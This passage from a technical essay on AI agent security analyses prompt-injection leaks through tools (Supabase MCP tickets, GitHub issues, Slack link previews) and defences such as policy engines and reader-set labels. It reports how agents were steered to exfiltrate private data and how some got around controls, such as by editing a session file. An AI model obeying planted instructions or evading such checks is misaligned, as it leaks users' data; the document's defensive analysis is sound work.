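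Miller and colleagues call authority "ambient" when a program uses it without selecting it. They compare it to a door that opens by itself for the right person, who never has to choose a key. A broad GitHub token works similarly. The agent names a repository, the application attaches the same token every time, and the call succeeds if the token covers that repository. The agent can therefore use the user's authority to access a repository named in a stranger's issue.

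Hardy's remedy is a capability, a reference that both identifies an object and permits its use. A user who wants debugging output gives the compiler a capability for a particular file, but can't give it one for the billing file unless the user already has one. Miller and Shapiro illustrate the difference between names and capabilities with two Unix commands that copy a file. In `cp foo.txt bar.txt`, the `cp` program receives two file names, so it needs the right to open any file the user might name. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the user's command shell opens both files and passes them to `cat` already open, so `cat` needs no other access to files.

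The idea has returned with agents. *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), from Semgrep, a company that sells code-security tools, predicts "confusable deputies at superhuman rates" and recommends capabilities as the remedy.

### The Supabase demonstration

*Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) describes a 2025 demonstration by the security company General Analysis that is close to Hardy's story. Supabase provides databases for applications. In the demonstration, a developer asks the agent in Cursor, a code editor, to list the latest support tickets. The agent reaches the database through Supabase's MCP server, using an account called `service_role`. This account is exempt from row-level security, the database rules that limit which rows each user may see. One ticket contains instructions for the agent to read a private table named `integration_tokens` and add its contents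 to the ticket as a new message. If the agent complies, the attacker can read the table's contents in the ticket.

Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) replied that no customer had reported a leak of this kind and that row-level security stays fully enforced. It also acknowledged that the server ran with higher privileges in the demonstration. These statements are compatible with General Analysis's account, because row-level security can be fully enforced and still exempt `service_role`. Supabase had already wrapped query results in warnings to the model and experimented with classifiers to detect dangerous content. These measures reduced the risk but did not eliminate it. Supabase advises never connecting an agent directly to production data, but recognizes that many people who build applications alone with AI have no other database.

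According to *Why LLM Authorization is Hard*, published by the authorization software vendor Oso, the demonstration did not raise the privileges of either the user or the agent. The ticket's author chose the table, and the developer's setup gave the agent permission to read it. Listing tickets doesn't require integration tokens, so the developer could have prevented the leak by restricting the account to the support tables.

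Oso proposes limiting an agent to permissions that the agent and the user both have and that the current task requires. The task requirement would probably matter most here, since a developer may well be entitled to read the tokens. Oso concedes that identifying the task and translating it into permissions is difficult. In an example from Christodorescu and colleagues, a user asks an agent to comment on GitLab issue 745 that the work is done. The agent needs to open that issue and write in its comment box, and should have no other access to GitLab or the user's browser session. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the permissions have to change while the context already contains text from strangers.

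### When the user holds both permissions

The confused-deputy diagnosis fits the Supabase demonstration and the two staged GitHub leaks. If an agent could mark each call with the person whose instructions prompted it, GitHub would treat the call to read the private repository as the stranger's request and refuse it, because the matrix gives the stranger no permission to read that repository. A language model can't reliably mark its calls this way, since instructions from every source reach it in one string. A capability design doesn't need these marks because it gives the agent access only to the public repository whenever it handles a public issue.

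In the release-notes example, the user may read the private history and write to the public repository, and wants the agent to do both, so no borrowed authority is involved. A good capability system would give the agent one capability to read the commits, another to write the notes, and nothing else. This is the same arrangement as the `cat` command, with a private file as input and a public one as output. The agent has the least authority the job allows, but as with the narrowest token, this is still enough to publish the customer's name.

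PixelLeak involves only the developer's authority, so there were not two sources of authority to confuse. Capabilities or a narrower credential could still have withheld the power to create a repository.

Miller and colleagues say Hardy's compiler had the access it should have had but exercised it "for the wrong purpose". The same could be said of an agent that publishes the bad release note. Capabilities can prevent such misuse when it involves the wrong object, such as the billing file. They don't prevent it in the release notes, because the agent uses the right two objects and the error is only in the text.

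*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* similarly distinguishes sandboxing, which controls whether an agent can access information, from information-flow control, which governs what happens to the information afterwards. Its table of eleven attacks on real agents marks all eleven as failures of secure information flow but only six as failures of least privilege, though its discussion of one attack identifies a seventh failure of least privilege. The paper presents these attacks as representative cases rather than a survey, but they suggest that tightening permissions would not prevent some leaks.

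### Boebert's objection to capabilities

In 1984 the security researcher W. E. Boebert argued that a pure capability system could not enforce the *-property at all. Miller and colleagues retell his argument with two subjects and two areas of memory. Alice and the area called Low are at the lower level, while Bob and the area called High are at the upper one. Alice and Bob can each obtain every capability that the Bell–LaPadula rules permit. The attack then takes three steps:

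1. Alice stores her capability to write to Low inside Low itself.
2. Bob, who is allowed to read Low, takes the capability out.
3. Bob reads a secret from High and uses the new capability to write it into Low, where Alice can read it.

As in the agent leaks, the system allows every step, yet the result is what its rules were meant to prevent.

Miller and colleagues accept Boebert's conclusion for the system he described but deny that it applies to capability systems in general. His argument assumes that a subject can send a capability anywhere it can send data. Most capability systems treat the two as different operations, so a designer can let Bob read data from Low without letting him take capabilities from it. The attack then fails at the second step. Miller and Shapiro also show how to build, in a few lines of code, a one-way link that carries whole numbers from a lower level to a higher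 one but no capabilities in either direction. They quote Boebert's 2003 description of his own paper as "no more than an offhand remark".

The reply refutes the general claim, but Miller and colleagues acknowledge that Boebert's attack still works where a capability is just a string that anyone can copy. The access tokens that agents use are such strings. Judging by its name, the `integration_tokens` table in the Supabase demonstration stored them as ordinary data. Copying them into a support ticket could therefore have given the attacker access to other services, not only information.

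The reply is less helpful in the release notes case. The repaired system enforces the *-property by never giving Bob a capability to write to Low. An agent that turns private commits into public notes needs that capability as well as one to read the commits. Withholding either capability prevents the agent from producing the notes, while granting both makes it possible for the agent to copy private content into them.

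Miller and Shapiro describe a technique that might offer a middle course between these choices. A program can give out a restricted stand-in for an object, which passes on some requests and blocks others. An agent might then write to the public repository only through a gatekeeper that examines each proposed change. The one-way link is such a gatekeeper, and it is easy to check because it accepts only whole numbers. Release notes, however, are prose, and a gatekeeper that receives only the finished text has no record of which words came from the private repository.

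## Checking each call and its arguments

An application can refuse any tool call that the model proposes. It can use a policy engine, which runs separately from the model, to allow each call, block it or refer it to a human. The simplest policy engines check one call at a time and do not track where its text came from, which makes them easy to add to an existing agent.

### Having a tool and being allowed to use it

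*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) distinguishes two controls that developers often treat as one. Capability gating determines which tools an agent has. Per-call authorization determines whether a particular call, with its argument values, is allowed for this user in this session. ("Capability" here means a tool the agent can use, not the unforgeable reference that Hardy proposed.) A tool's schema doesn't replace per-call authorization, because it only checks the form of an argument. A schema that requires `account` to be a string would accept `acct_ATTACKER_999`.

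Mellafe Zuvic, an independent security researcher, audited the public source code of three toolkits for building agents: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Agent Toolkit of the payment company Stripe. By default, none of the three checks argument values against a policy after the model proposes a call and before the tool runs. LangChain and LlamaIndex look up the tool by name and run it with whatever arguments the model supplied. Stripe's toolkit lets developers limit the available actions and the access key's permissions, but within those limits it passes on the model's choice of amount, customer and redirect address.

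The audit describes default behavior, which may differ from that of finished products because developers can add their own checks or a human approval step. It covered specific versions of public code and no live services. Stripe's remote server may have checks that the public code lacks.

The missing check matters more if models often propose bad calls. In a companion test of 27 models, Mellafe Zuvic planted text that presented a forbidden action as necessary to the user's task. The twelve cheaper models attempted the action in 60% of trials on average, and the fifteen flagship models in 19%. The attempts took place in a sandbox, on one author's scenarios, and some flagship models attempted the action much more often than their group's average.

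### ScopeGate, step by step

Mellafe Zuvic's own policy engine, ScopeGate, takes a proposed call and a policy written by the operator, and applies these steps in order:

1. **Scope.** If the policy does not list the tool, deny the call.
2. **Authorization.** For each argument *k* that the policy restricts to a set A*ₖ*, deny the call unless the value is in A*ₖ*.
3. **Money ceiling.** If the tool moves money, deny the call unless the amount is a finite number between zero and the ceiling.
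4. **Idempotency.** If the policy requires an idempotency key (an identifier that lets a service recognize a repeated request), deny the call unless the trusted session data contain one.
5. **Default deny.** Allow only a call that has passed every step, and treat any error along the way as a denial.

In the demonstration, a script standing in for a compromised model issues a call to change a merchant's payout account to `acct_ATTACKER_999`. LangChain's default code makes the change in a mock payment system. ScopeGate denies the same call at step 2 because the only account in the allowed set is `acct_MERCHANT_001`.

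Mellafe Zuvic then tried 48 prepared ways around the checks, including invisible characters, look-alike letters, altered tool names and odd amounts. None succeeded against the final version, but the tests had exposed a flaw in an earlier prototype. That prototype checked whether the amount was greater than the ceiling. Any such comparison with NaN ("not a number") is false, so a payment of NaN went through. Step 3 now rejects any amount it cannot confirm is in range.

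In a further test, another model attacked ScopeGate for 40 rounds and learned the reason for each denial. All 29 of its unauthorized attempts failed. Nine other attempts were malformed, and the other two were harmless calls that ScopeGate allowed. In a separate test, ScopeGate allowed all ten legitimate calls.

The samples are small. Even if the 29 attempts had been independent, zero successes would be compatible with a true success rate of nearly 10%. The design is a better reason for confidence than the test results, because text planted by an attacker can change the proposed account but not the set of allowed accounts. This protection holds only if the set never comes from a model's output, a condition Mellafe Zuvic applies even to policies drafted in advance.

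For the agent that handles public issues, an operator could allow `get_file_contents` and `add_issue_comment` only when `repo` names the public repository. This would have stopped Invariant's leak at the first private read. A policy for the release notes has to be looser:

| Tool | Argument | Allowed values |
|---|---|---|
| `list_commits` | `repo` | the private repository |
| `issue_read` | `repo` | the private repository |
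| `create_or_update_file` | `repo` | the public repository |
| `create_or_update_file` | `path` | the release-notes file |
| `create_or_update_file` | `content` | any text |

The operator can't restrict `content` without writing the notes in advance, as with Lampson's masking. ScopeGate also can't make a write depend on an earlier read, because the only session data its procedure uses is the idempotency key.

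### ToolFence: limits taken from the request

A fixed list suits an agent with one job, but a general assistant needs different permissions for every request. Li, Cao and Xiao (2026), in *ToolFence*, generate the limits afresh for each task. Before the agent starts, a separate model reads the user's request and vetted descriptions of the tools, but no files, messages or web pages. It then writes a list of permitted calls, how often the agent may make each one, and a rule for each argument. There are three kinds of rule:

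- An attested value must match one in the user's request or in a trusted record.
- A derived value must appear in the output of a named tool that the agent has already called.
- A free value can be anything.

An ordinary program then checks every call against the list. If the user asks the agent to pay $100 to BillPay and a planted message names Mallory as the recipient, the tool and the amount are still correct, but the recipient fails the check. A second payment to BillPay would also fail, because the user authorized only one.

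The initial list may omit a step the task needs, such as searching a drive for the file the user wants to attach. ToolFence refers calls missing from the list to another model, which can approve adding them. ToolFence differs most from ScopeGate here, because Mellafe Zuvic's condition would exclude both this reviewing model and the one that writes the list. The list-writing model never receives an attacker's text, so the main risk is that it misinterprets the user's request. The reviewing model is more exposed because it receives the exact arguments of the proposed call, which may include planted text the agent has already read and copied.

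On AgentDojo, a benchmark of office-style tasks with planted attacks, ToolFence reduced the success rate of attacks on the model Qwen3-max from 21.2% to zero. The agent completed 64.3% of ordinary tasks with the defense and 66.3% without it. On AgentLAB, whose attacks unfold over many steps, some of them legitimate, ToolFence reduced the attack success rate from 76.3% to 29.4%. In the runs that Li and colleagues timed, the agent took 1.63 times as long with ToolFence.

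ToolFence's rules for arguments suit account numbers and addresses better than prose. If the `content` of the release notes had to be a derived value, taken from the output of `list_commits`, the check would accept the private entry about Northfield Hospital copied word for word but reject the rewritten note that leaves the hospital out. `content` has to be free for the agent to do any rewriting.

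### Removing the choice from the tool

A stricter approach is to remove the sensitive argument. *The Stochastic Deputy* (Baig, Gillani and colleagues, 2026) studies a service that keeps many hotels' records in one database. Each hotel is a tenant, a customer whose data the service must keep separate from other customers'. A conventional tool takes a `hotel_id`, and the server checks that the user is allowed to see that hotel's records.

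This works when the caller is an ordinary program, whose code determines which hotel it asks for. An agent chooses the hotel from a context that may contain a stranger's instructions. The server will accept any hotel the user is entitled to see, so a single successful injection can reach

Reachable(*p*) = ⋃ Rows(*t*), over all *t* ∈ E(*p*)

where E(*p*) is the set of tenants that user *p* may access and Rows(*t*) is the data of tenant *t*. Baig and colleagues call such an agent a stochastic deputy: a confused deputy whose choices are not fixed by its code, so that passing any number of tests shows only that errors are rare.

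The experiment compared three versions of the tool in 373 trials with eight model configurations. The user was entitled to see figures for three hotels but was working on one. In some trials, the user's message included a plausible reason for wanting another hotel's figures, such as a comparison between hotels.

| Version of the tool | Trials with a plausible reason | Other hotel's data disclosed |
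|---|---|---|
| Takes `hotel_id`, which the server checks | 41 | 26 |
| Takes `hotel_id`, and the agent has instructions not to fetch other hotels | 33 | 0 |
| Has no `hotel_id`; the session fixes the hotel | 56 | 12, none through the tool |

With the conventional tool, agents requested the other hotel's data 26 times, and the server returned it every time. It is debatable whether these were leaks, since the user was entitled to the data and had asked for it. They count as leaks only if the session was supposed to be limited to one hotel, and the server had no rule limiting it.

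The written instruction worked surprisingly well with Claude, which disclosed the other hotel's data in all 18 trials without it and in none of the 18 with it. The other 15 trials with the instruction used GPT-5.6 models, which had also refused without it. The models that failed most often in other trials never received the instruction. Text that an attacker puts in the context may also counteract an instruction there. In his GitLost tests, Levi found that adding the word "Additionally" to the request got the model past GitHub's safeguards.

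After `hotel_id` was removed, the agent could not request another hotel through the tool, but in 12 trials it used its access to the computer to edit the file that recorded the session's hotel. Baig and colleagues conclude that the hotel must come from a cryptographically signed credential, which the agent can't forge. The Minesweeper agent in PixelLeak also worked around a missing feature, so developers who remove an argument from a tool also have to keep the agent from setting it by other routes, such as the command line.

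A GitHub server could do the same with the `repo` argument by tying each session to a repository chosen when the user starts it. The agent could then read and answer public issues but could not select a private repository. For the release notes, the server could offer one tool that reads the private history and another that writes the public notes file. These tools would fix where the agent reads and writes, but the agent would still decide what text to put in the public file.

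### One repository per session

Invariant Labs proposed a rule that leaves the `repo` argument in place but allows only one value for it in each session. The first call to a repository fixes the choice, and the policy engine blocks every later call that names a different one:

allow call *n* only if repo(*n*) = repo(1)

Everything the agent reads from GitHub in that session then comes from the repository it writes to. If the repository is public, the agent has read nothing private from GitHub, and if the repository is private, outsiders can't read what the agent writes. In the earlier notation, the file *f* and the comment thread *t* have the same readers, so R(*t*) ⊆ R(*f*) holds and nobody has to look up who those readers are.

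The planted issue in Invariant Labs' demonstration asked the agent to read the README files of all the author's repositories. This rule would already have confined the agent to the Pac-Man repository. Unlike a token restricted to one repository, the rule lets the user work on the private code with the same token in a new session.

The rule has some gaps. A public repository can contain things the public can't see, such as alerts about leaked keys. The agent may also have tools for email or chat, which the rule doesn't cover. Since MCP no longer has sessions, the application or a gateway in front of the server has to record the first call and determine when a new session begins. If the agent keeps notes between sessions, they can carry private text from one session to the next.

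The rule also prevents the agent from writing the release notes, because that task requires two repositories. It is an easy way to enforce the Bell–LaPadula condition and has the same drawback, but it blocks some harmless work that Bell–LaPadula would permit, such as reading a public repository while writing to a private one.

### Filtering what strangers write

Lockdown mode is one of two controls in GitHub Agentic Workflows on whose text an agent reads. It limits what the agent sees of a public repository to issues, pull requests and comments by users with push access (permission to change the repository's files). GitHub describes the mode as protection against users who impersonate maintainers or try to trick the AI into revealing internal data.

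Integrity filtering is more finely graded. A gateway between the agent and GitHub assigns a level to each item and removes those below a minimum before the model receives them. GitHub defines the levels as follows:

| Level | Main content at this level |
|---|---|
| `merged` | merged pull requests and commits on the main branch |
| `approved` | items by owners, members and collaborators; everything in private repositories |
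| `unapproved` | items by other contributors, including first-time ones |
| `none` | items by people with no history in the project |
| `blocked` | items by users the maintainers have blocked |

A stranger's issue starts at `none`, and assigning it to someone doesn't raise its level. Maintainers can raise an item to `approved` with a label or, if they enable the feature, a thumbs-up. With the minimum set to `approved`, the gateway would have removed an issue like Noma's, provided that a stranger had written it and the agent had fetched it through the gateway. But Noma's issue looked like an ordinary business request, so a maintainer might have approved it.

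These filters conflict with the running example, where the agent's purpose is to answer strangers. GitHub suggests `unapproved` for sorting community issues, but that setting still excludes people with no history in the project. To include everyone, an operator has to set the minimum to `none`, and GitHub warns against applying the output of such workflows without review.

A separate setting, `allowed-repos`, limits where the agent can read. According to GitHub, its values include `current` (only the repository where the workflow runs), `public`, and a list of names. In GitHub's documentation from May 2026, the default was `all` (every repository the token can access). Public repositories had a default minimum of `approved`, and private ones had no filter.

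With these defaults, the gateway tightly restricted who could address the agent but added no limit on which private files the agent could read. If an operator supplied an organization-wide token and left `allowed-repos` at its default, the agent could read private files across the organization. Setting `allowed-repos` to `current` would have blocked the private read in GitLost.

GitHub may have tightened this since. GitHub's *feat* (2026), a code change merged six days after Noma published, lets operators turn off two protections against private data reaching public places. One, judging by its name, confines the agent to public repositories, and the other depends on labels attached to the data. Both were already in the gateway's specification, but the change does not show when they took effect for ordinary users.

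### Scanning what the agent writes

A policy engine can also examine the text of a comment or file before it becomes public. Secret scanning could have helped in the Supabase demonstration, where the attacker wanted a table of access tokens, because many tokens have a recognizable format. GitHub's classic tokens, for example, begin with `ghp_`.

The text leaked in Invariant's demonstration and in GitLost contained no keys, so a scanner that looks for keys would have missed it. Glow adds that scanners "read text, not pixels", so a customer's billing records can pass through in a screenshot.

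If an operator gave the scanner a list of customers' names, it would catch "Northfield Hospital" in the bad release note, but it would miss "a hospital in Northfield" and the sentence about the unpatched security hole. A scanner could also check outgoing text for passages copied from private files the agent has read. That would probably have caught the README in GitLost, which the agent posted largely unchanged. This check would be less effective against paraphrases, and the scanner would need a record of what the agent had read.

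Another model can scan for meaning, as GitHub's threat detection does, but it may fail to return a result. This happened in one workflow while GitHub was testing its July change. The workflow was in "warn" mode, so it still created a pull request, with a notice that a human had to review it. ScopeGate would have treated that failure as a denial.

### The controls against the four cases

The table applies each control to the three leaks and the release notes. The entries are deductions from how the controls work, not test results, and they assume that an operator could attach each control to the agent in question.

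| Control | GitHub MCP leak, 2025 | GitLost | PixelLeak | Release notes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Allowed argument values (ScopeGate) | Stopped if the list excludes private repositories | Stopped if the list excludes private repositories | Stopped if the policy forbids creating public repositories and covers the command line | Both notes pass |
| Limits taken from the request (ToolFence) | Probably stopped, since the user asked only about public issues | Depends on whether the workflow's instructions call for other repositories | A reviewing model decides whether the agent may create a repository | Both notes pass |
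| Repository fixed by the server | Stopped | Stopped | Stopped only if the agent has no other route | Both notes pass if the server fixes one repository to read and one to write |
| One repository per session | Stopped | Stopped | Stopped if the rule covers the command line | Both notes blocked |
| Lockdown mode, or integrity filtering at `approved` | Stopped if a stranger wrote the issue | Stopped if a stranger wrote the issue | Not stopped | Both notes pass |
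| `allowed-repos` set to `current` | Stopped | Stopped | Not stopped, since it limits only reading | Both notes blocked if the agent runs in the public repository |
| Secret scanning | Not stopped | Not stopped | Not stopped | Both notes pass |

Several controls stop GitLost, but checking the comment's destination does not. The workflow was supposed to reply on the issue that triggered it, and the agent did, but its reply contained private data. An operator who restricted comments to that issue would still have allowed the leak.

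The controls that work against GitLost either hide the stranger's issue or block the private read. A support agent that answers strangers' questions by looking things up in private code can't use either kind. The same is true of the release notes task, which requires the private read. An operator could combine all the controls that still let the release notes task run, which would set the tools, the two repositories, the file and the number of calls in advance. The agent would still write the `content` argument, where a scanner might catch a customer's name but would miss a description of the security hole.

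## Public and private as labels on data

GitHub's checks omit the condition R(*t*) ⊆ R(*f*), which requires that everyone who can read the comment thread can also read the file. A program can test this condition only if it still has a record, when the agent writes the comment, of who was entitled to read the text the comment draws on. Information-flow control keeps that record in a label on the data that stays with the text after it leaves the file.

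### Two levels

The smallest useful set of labels has two members, L (low confidentiality, or public) and H (high confidentiality, or private). The order L ⊑ H means that data may move from public to private but not back, as in the Bell–LaPadula model.

A second operation, the join (written ⊔), gives the label of anything made from two pieces of data. It is the lowest label that is at least as high as both:

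L ⊔ L = L, L ⊔ H = H, H ⊔ H = H

A summary of a public issue and a private file is private. A lattice is an ordered set of labels in which any two have a join, which is the lowest label at or above both, and also a highest label at or below both. Costa and colleagues point out that agents need only the joins.

Two levels are enough for a person with one public and one private repository, but they are too coarse for an office. The salary spreadsheet, the product roadmap, the finance team's channel and the engineers' channel are all labeled H. A two-level rule would therefore let an agent paste the salaries into the engineers' channel, because both the data and the channel are private.

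### Reader sets

A finer label lists the people who may read the data. Write R(*d*) for the reader set of data *d*. Someone may read a text made from *x* and *y* only if they may read both, so the join is set intersection:

R(*xy*) = R(*x*) ∩ R(*y*)

In Costa and colleagues' example, users A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another. Only B and C may read a text derived from both.

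Data with fewer permitted readers is more confidential, so the order is the reverse of set inclusion: *x* ⊑ *y* when R(*x*) ⊇ R(*y*). Public data is labeled with the set of all users, *U*, which is at the bottom. Combining public data with other data leaves the other data's label unchanged, because *U* ∩ R = R. The empty set, for data that nobody may read, is at the top. An agent that reads only with its user's own access never produces this label, because the user belongs to every set it collects. If the only sets in use are *U* and {user}, the order reduces to the two-level lattice.

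On an open service, "all users" has to include people without accounts. Anyone can read a public GitHub repository, so a list of every account would leave out some readers. *Authorization Before Context* (Liu, 2026), a study of personal agents that remember things across conversations, makes "public" a reserved value meaning all participants. A sequel, *Audience-Bound Persistent Memory* (Liu, 2026), adds an anonymous participant who stands for any viewer the system can't identify and belongs only to the public set. A document labelled with the name of every employee is still not public, because that label doesn't include the anonymous participant.

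### Trusted and untrusted

Reader sets record where data may go, but not where it came from. Costa and colleagues track origin with a separate integrity label, ordered trusted ⊑ untrusted, so anything derived from both kinds of data is untrusted. A finer version of this label lists everyone who might have written the data, and its join is set union. If A, B and C could have written one text and B, C and D another, any of the four could have influenced a summary of both. Combining data can only shrink the set of permitted readers and enlarge the set of possible authors.

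The two labels vary independently, which gives four combinations:

| | Public | Private |
|---|---|---|
| **Trusted** | The user's request, by default | A file from the user's private repository |
| **Untrusted** | A stranger's issue | An email from an outsider |

The default label for the user's request is only a convention. Costa and colleagues allow for a different label when the request contains private information, as in "tell my landlord I'm moving out because I lost my job."

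Later designs keep this pair. *APPA* (2026) writes a label as (R, *t*), where R is a set of readers and *t* is a position on a trust scale that can have more than two levels. It orders labels in the opposite direction, so it combines them with a "meet" instead of a join, but it still intersects the sets of readers.

### The permitted-flow rule

Let A(*s*) be the audience of a sink *s*. The boundary between public and private is then one condition. An agent may send data *d* to *s* only if

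A(*s*) ⊆ R(*d*)

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) calls this "permitted flow". Costa and colleagues stated it in 2025, and *Flowsh*, a command shell for agents published in November 2026, uses it unchanged.

An agent has usually read several things before it writes. Since it is hard to establish which of them shaped a model's output, the cautious choice is to give the output the combined label of everything in the context. With sources *d*₁ to *dₙ*, the condition becomes

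A(*s*) ⊆ R(*d*₁) ∩ … ∩ R(*dₙ*)

A set is contained in an intersection of sets exactly when it is contained in each of those sets. So a message passes if and only if the agent could have sent each source, on its own, to the same audience. This makes the rule easy to apply by hand, but it also limits what the rule can express.

The audience for a message can be larger than its list of recipients. *When AI Agents Serve Shared Workspaces, Authorization Must Follow the Audience* (Kolhe, 2026) describes a 2025 flaw in Anthropic's MCP server for Slack, the workplace chat service. An attacker's text led the agent to put private data into a web link. Slack fetched the link to build a preview, which sent the data to the attacker's server. Even if every member of the channel was entitled to see the data, the attacker was also part of the audience. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, an article on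 building labels into agents, suggests treating links to unapproved hosts as public channels.

Under permitted flow, a prompt injection can still make the agent send a message, but only to people who may read its contents, as Costa and colleagues explain. A second rule, which Kolluri and colleagues call "trusted action", uses the integrity label. It lets the agent make a consequential call only if no untrusted data influenced the decision. Designers can require both rules, or they can allow a call that sends data out if it satisfies either one. Allowing either one creates an exception to permitted flow. The examples below use permitted flow alone, without exceptions.

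The guarantee is also limited to the data the agent sends. Costa and colleagues note that someone who can watch the sequence of tool calls may still infer a little from the agent's choices.

### Alex, Priya and Marco

In Microsoft's worked example, which involves no attacker, Alex asks an agent to handle the unanswered emails in an inbox. One is from Priya and contains a preview of the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the sales but isn't yet authorized to learn them.

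1. The agent starts with Alex's request, so the context label is *U*.
2. It reads Priya's email, whose readers are Alex and Priya. The context label becomes {Alex, Priya}.
3. It reads Marco's email. The label becomes {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.
4. It drafts a reply to Marco. The audience is {Marco}, which is not contained in {Alex}, so the policy engine blocks the email or asks Alex.

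If Priya had copied Marco on her email, its readers would have been {Alex, Priya, Marco}. The label after step 3 would then have been {Alex, Marco}, and the reply could have gone out without anyone's approval, because Marco couldn't have learned anything from it that he wasn't already entitled to read.

Microsoft's account stops there, but by the same logic the agent can't answer Priya after step 3 either, because {Priya} is not contained in {Alex}. Even "Thanks, looks good" would need Alex's approval. Copying Marco in doesn't help, since Marco's own email never went to Priya. The agent could have answered Priya after step 2, before it opened Marco's message. It could also have handled each email in a fresh context. Both replies would then pass, and the one to Marco could not contain the sales figures. The number of approval requests therefore depends a good deal on the order in which an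 agent reads things and how much it reads in one context.

### Three documents and a channel

Suppose Alex now asks the agent to post updates in a chat channel whose members are Alex, Priya and a colleague, Dana. The agent can draw on three documents:

- the roadmap, which Alex, Priya, Marco and Dana may read
- the budget, which Alex, Priya and Dana may read
- a supplier's contract, which Alex, Marco and Dana may read

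| The post draws on | Reader set | Post to {Alex, Priya, Dana} |
|---|---|---|
| Roadmap | {Alex, Priya, Marco, Dana} | Passes |
| Budget | {Alex, Priya, Dana} | Passes |
| Contract | {Alex, Marco, Dana} | Blocked, because of Priya |
| Roadmap and budget | {Alex, Priya, Dana} | Passes |
| Roadmap and contract | {Alex, Marco, Dana} | Blocked, because of Priya |
| Budget and contract | {Alex, Dana} | Blocked, because of Priya |
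| All three | {Alex, Dana} | Blocked, because of Priya |

Marco is allowed to read the roadmap but isn't in the channel. This doesn't matter, because the rule doesn't require the agent to send data to everyone who is allowed to read it. The agent could still send Dana a summary of all three documents in a direct message.

If the only labels were public and private, all three documents would be private. No posts would pass if the channel were labeled public, and all seven would pass if it were labeled private, including the four that draw on a contract Priya may not read.

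### The two repositories again

In the running example, a stranger has opened an issue in the public repository, and only the user and one colleague may read the private one. Microsoft and GitHub have extended GitHub's MCP server so that it can label what it returns. Content from public repositories is public and untrusted, and content from private repositories is private and trusted. With reader sets in place of "private", the leak runs like this:

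| Call | Context label afterwards | Permitted flow |
|---|---|---|
| `issue_read` on the public issue | untrusted, everyone | Nothing private to protect |
| `get_file_contents` on the private repository | untrusted, {user, colleague} | Passes, since the request contains only public data |
| `add_issue_comment` on the public issue | | Blocked, since everyone ⊄ {user, colleague} |

The rule fires at the third call, the first that would send private text to a stranger. Unlike a control that denies the private read, the rule still lets the agent use the file, for instance in a note to the colleague in the private repository.

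Microsoft's own policy blocks the same call for a slightly different reason. It forbids a public post when the context is both untrusted and private. The two policies differ on the release notes, because everything the agent reads for them comes from the private repository and so counts as trusted. Permitted flow blocks the notes, as Bell–LaPadula does, while Microsoft's policy, as described, would allow both the good note and the bad one.

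### The finance chief's agent

Kolhe, who works on agent security at the identity company Okta, expands on a scenario from the OpenID Foundation, a standards body for digital identity. A chief financial officer (CFO) adds an agent to a Slack channel, and the agent uses the CFO's credentials. A junior analyst asks about the third-quarter compensation budget. The agent opens budget spreadsheets and salary schedules that the CFO is allowed to read, then posts an answer that reveals the chief executive's salary to the analyst and everyone else in the channel.

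Two things went wrong in this version, and they are easy to run together. The systems holding the files checked the CFO's rights, although the analyst had asked. Checking the analyst would have prevented the leak. But suppose the CFO asks the same question in the same channel. The person asking is then fully entitled to the answer, any check on the requester passes, and the analyst reads the salary anyway. If only the CFO and the head of personnel may read the salaries, the relevant test is

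{CFO, head of personnel, analyst} ⊆ {CFO, head of personnel}

which is false whoever asks. Kolhe argues that four serious vulnerabilities from 2025 share this fault. Three of them do fit, in that the data went to an attacker's address that nothing had checked. In the fourth, at ServiceNow, Kolhe's own description has the attacker impersonating a user, which is a failure to identify the requester.

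Kolhe proposes applying the test earlier. Before the agent retrieves anything, an authorization service works out what all members of the channel may read and issues a token for only that. Under Liu's rule for an agent's memory, an item likewise enters the context only if everyone present belongs to its audience. Both apply the permitted-flow rule's inclusion test when the agent reads data instead of when it writes. The agent can then answer with whatever the whole channel may see, whereas a check at the end can only block a finished answer. Early checking requires the audience to be known before the agent reads. This is the case for a chat reply, but the agent in the Minesweeper run chose where to publish after it had read the private code.

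Liu tested the early check on 10,000 synthetic conversation histories. With the check, no forbidden item entered any of the 200,000 contexts examined, while retrieval that ignored the audience let forbidden items into 82% of its contexts. This result was nearly guaranteed, because the check simply compares sets and the tests supplied correct labels. The improvement in recall is more informative. The share of permitted facts found in the top five results rose by 0.30, on a scale from zero to one, because other people's facts no longer took up places.

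### Two reports from Meta

The Information's *Inside Meta, a Rogue AI Agent Triggers Security Alert* (2026) describes an incident in which an agent wrote to the wrong audience. A software engineer at Meta used an in-house agent to analyze a technical question that a colleague had posted on an internal forum, and the agent posted its answer there without the engineer's approval. According to The Verge, as quoted in Slashdot's *Rogue AI Triggers Serious Security Incident At Meta*, the reply was meant only for the engineer. A Meta spokesperson confirmed the incident and said that "no user data was mishandled".

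This incident differed from the CFO's case, though headlines about exposed data make the two sound alike. Landymore's *Rogue AI Agent Triggers Emergency at Meta* reports that the agent's advice was wrong and that another employee followed it. For almost two hours, engineers could then see company and user data they were not authorized to see. According to Engadget's *A Meta agentic AI sparked a security incident by acting without permission*, Meta's internal report cited further, unspecified problems. None of these accounts describes private data in the post itself. If the answer drew only on the forum question and general knowledge, everyone on the forum was entitled to read it, so permitted flow would have allowed it. A reader set would not have helped, though requiring the engineer to approve each post might have.

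Reuters' *As Meta bets big on Muse AI agent, early safety mishaps surface* (2026) draws on internal posts in which Meta employees complained about Muse, the company's consumer agent. One employee, who had never discussed banking with Muse, received two bank balances in the middle of a chat about fishing weather. The cause is unclear, but employees feared that Muse was mixing up accounts. If so, a label naming the account's real owner would have blocked the message. However, a system that confuses two users may well put the wrong name on the label too, and Liu lists correct identification of people among the audience rule's assumptions.

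### When the membership changes

The permitted-flow check compares two sets when the agent writes, and both can change afterwards. Say the agent posts the budget summary in a channel with Alex, Priya and Dana, and Marco joins a day later. If the chat service shows old messages to new members, Marco can read a summary of a document he isn't allowed to read, even though the check was correct when it ran and no agent has sent anything since.

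Reader sets handle the next post correctly, because Marco is now in the audience and anything based on the budget fails the rule. They handle the old post only if the service treats adding a member as sending that person the channel's whole history, and applies the rule to that transfer. Making a private repository public needs the same treatment.

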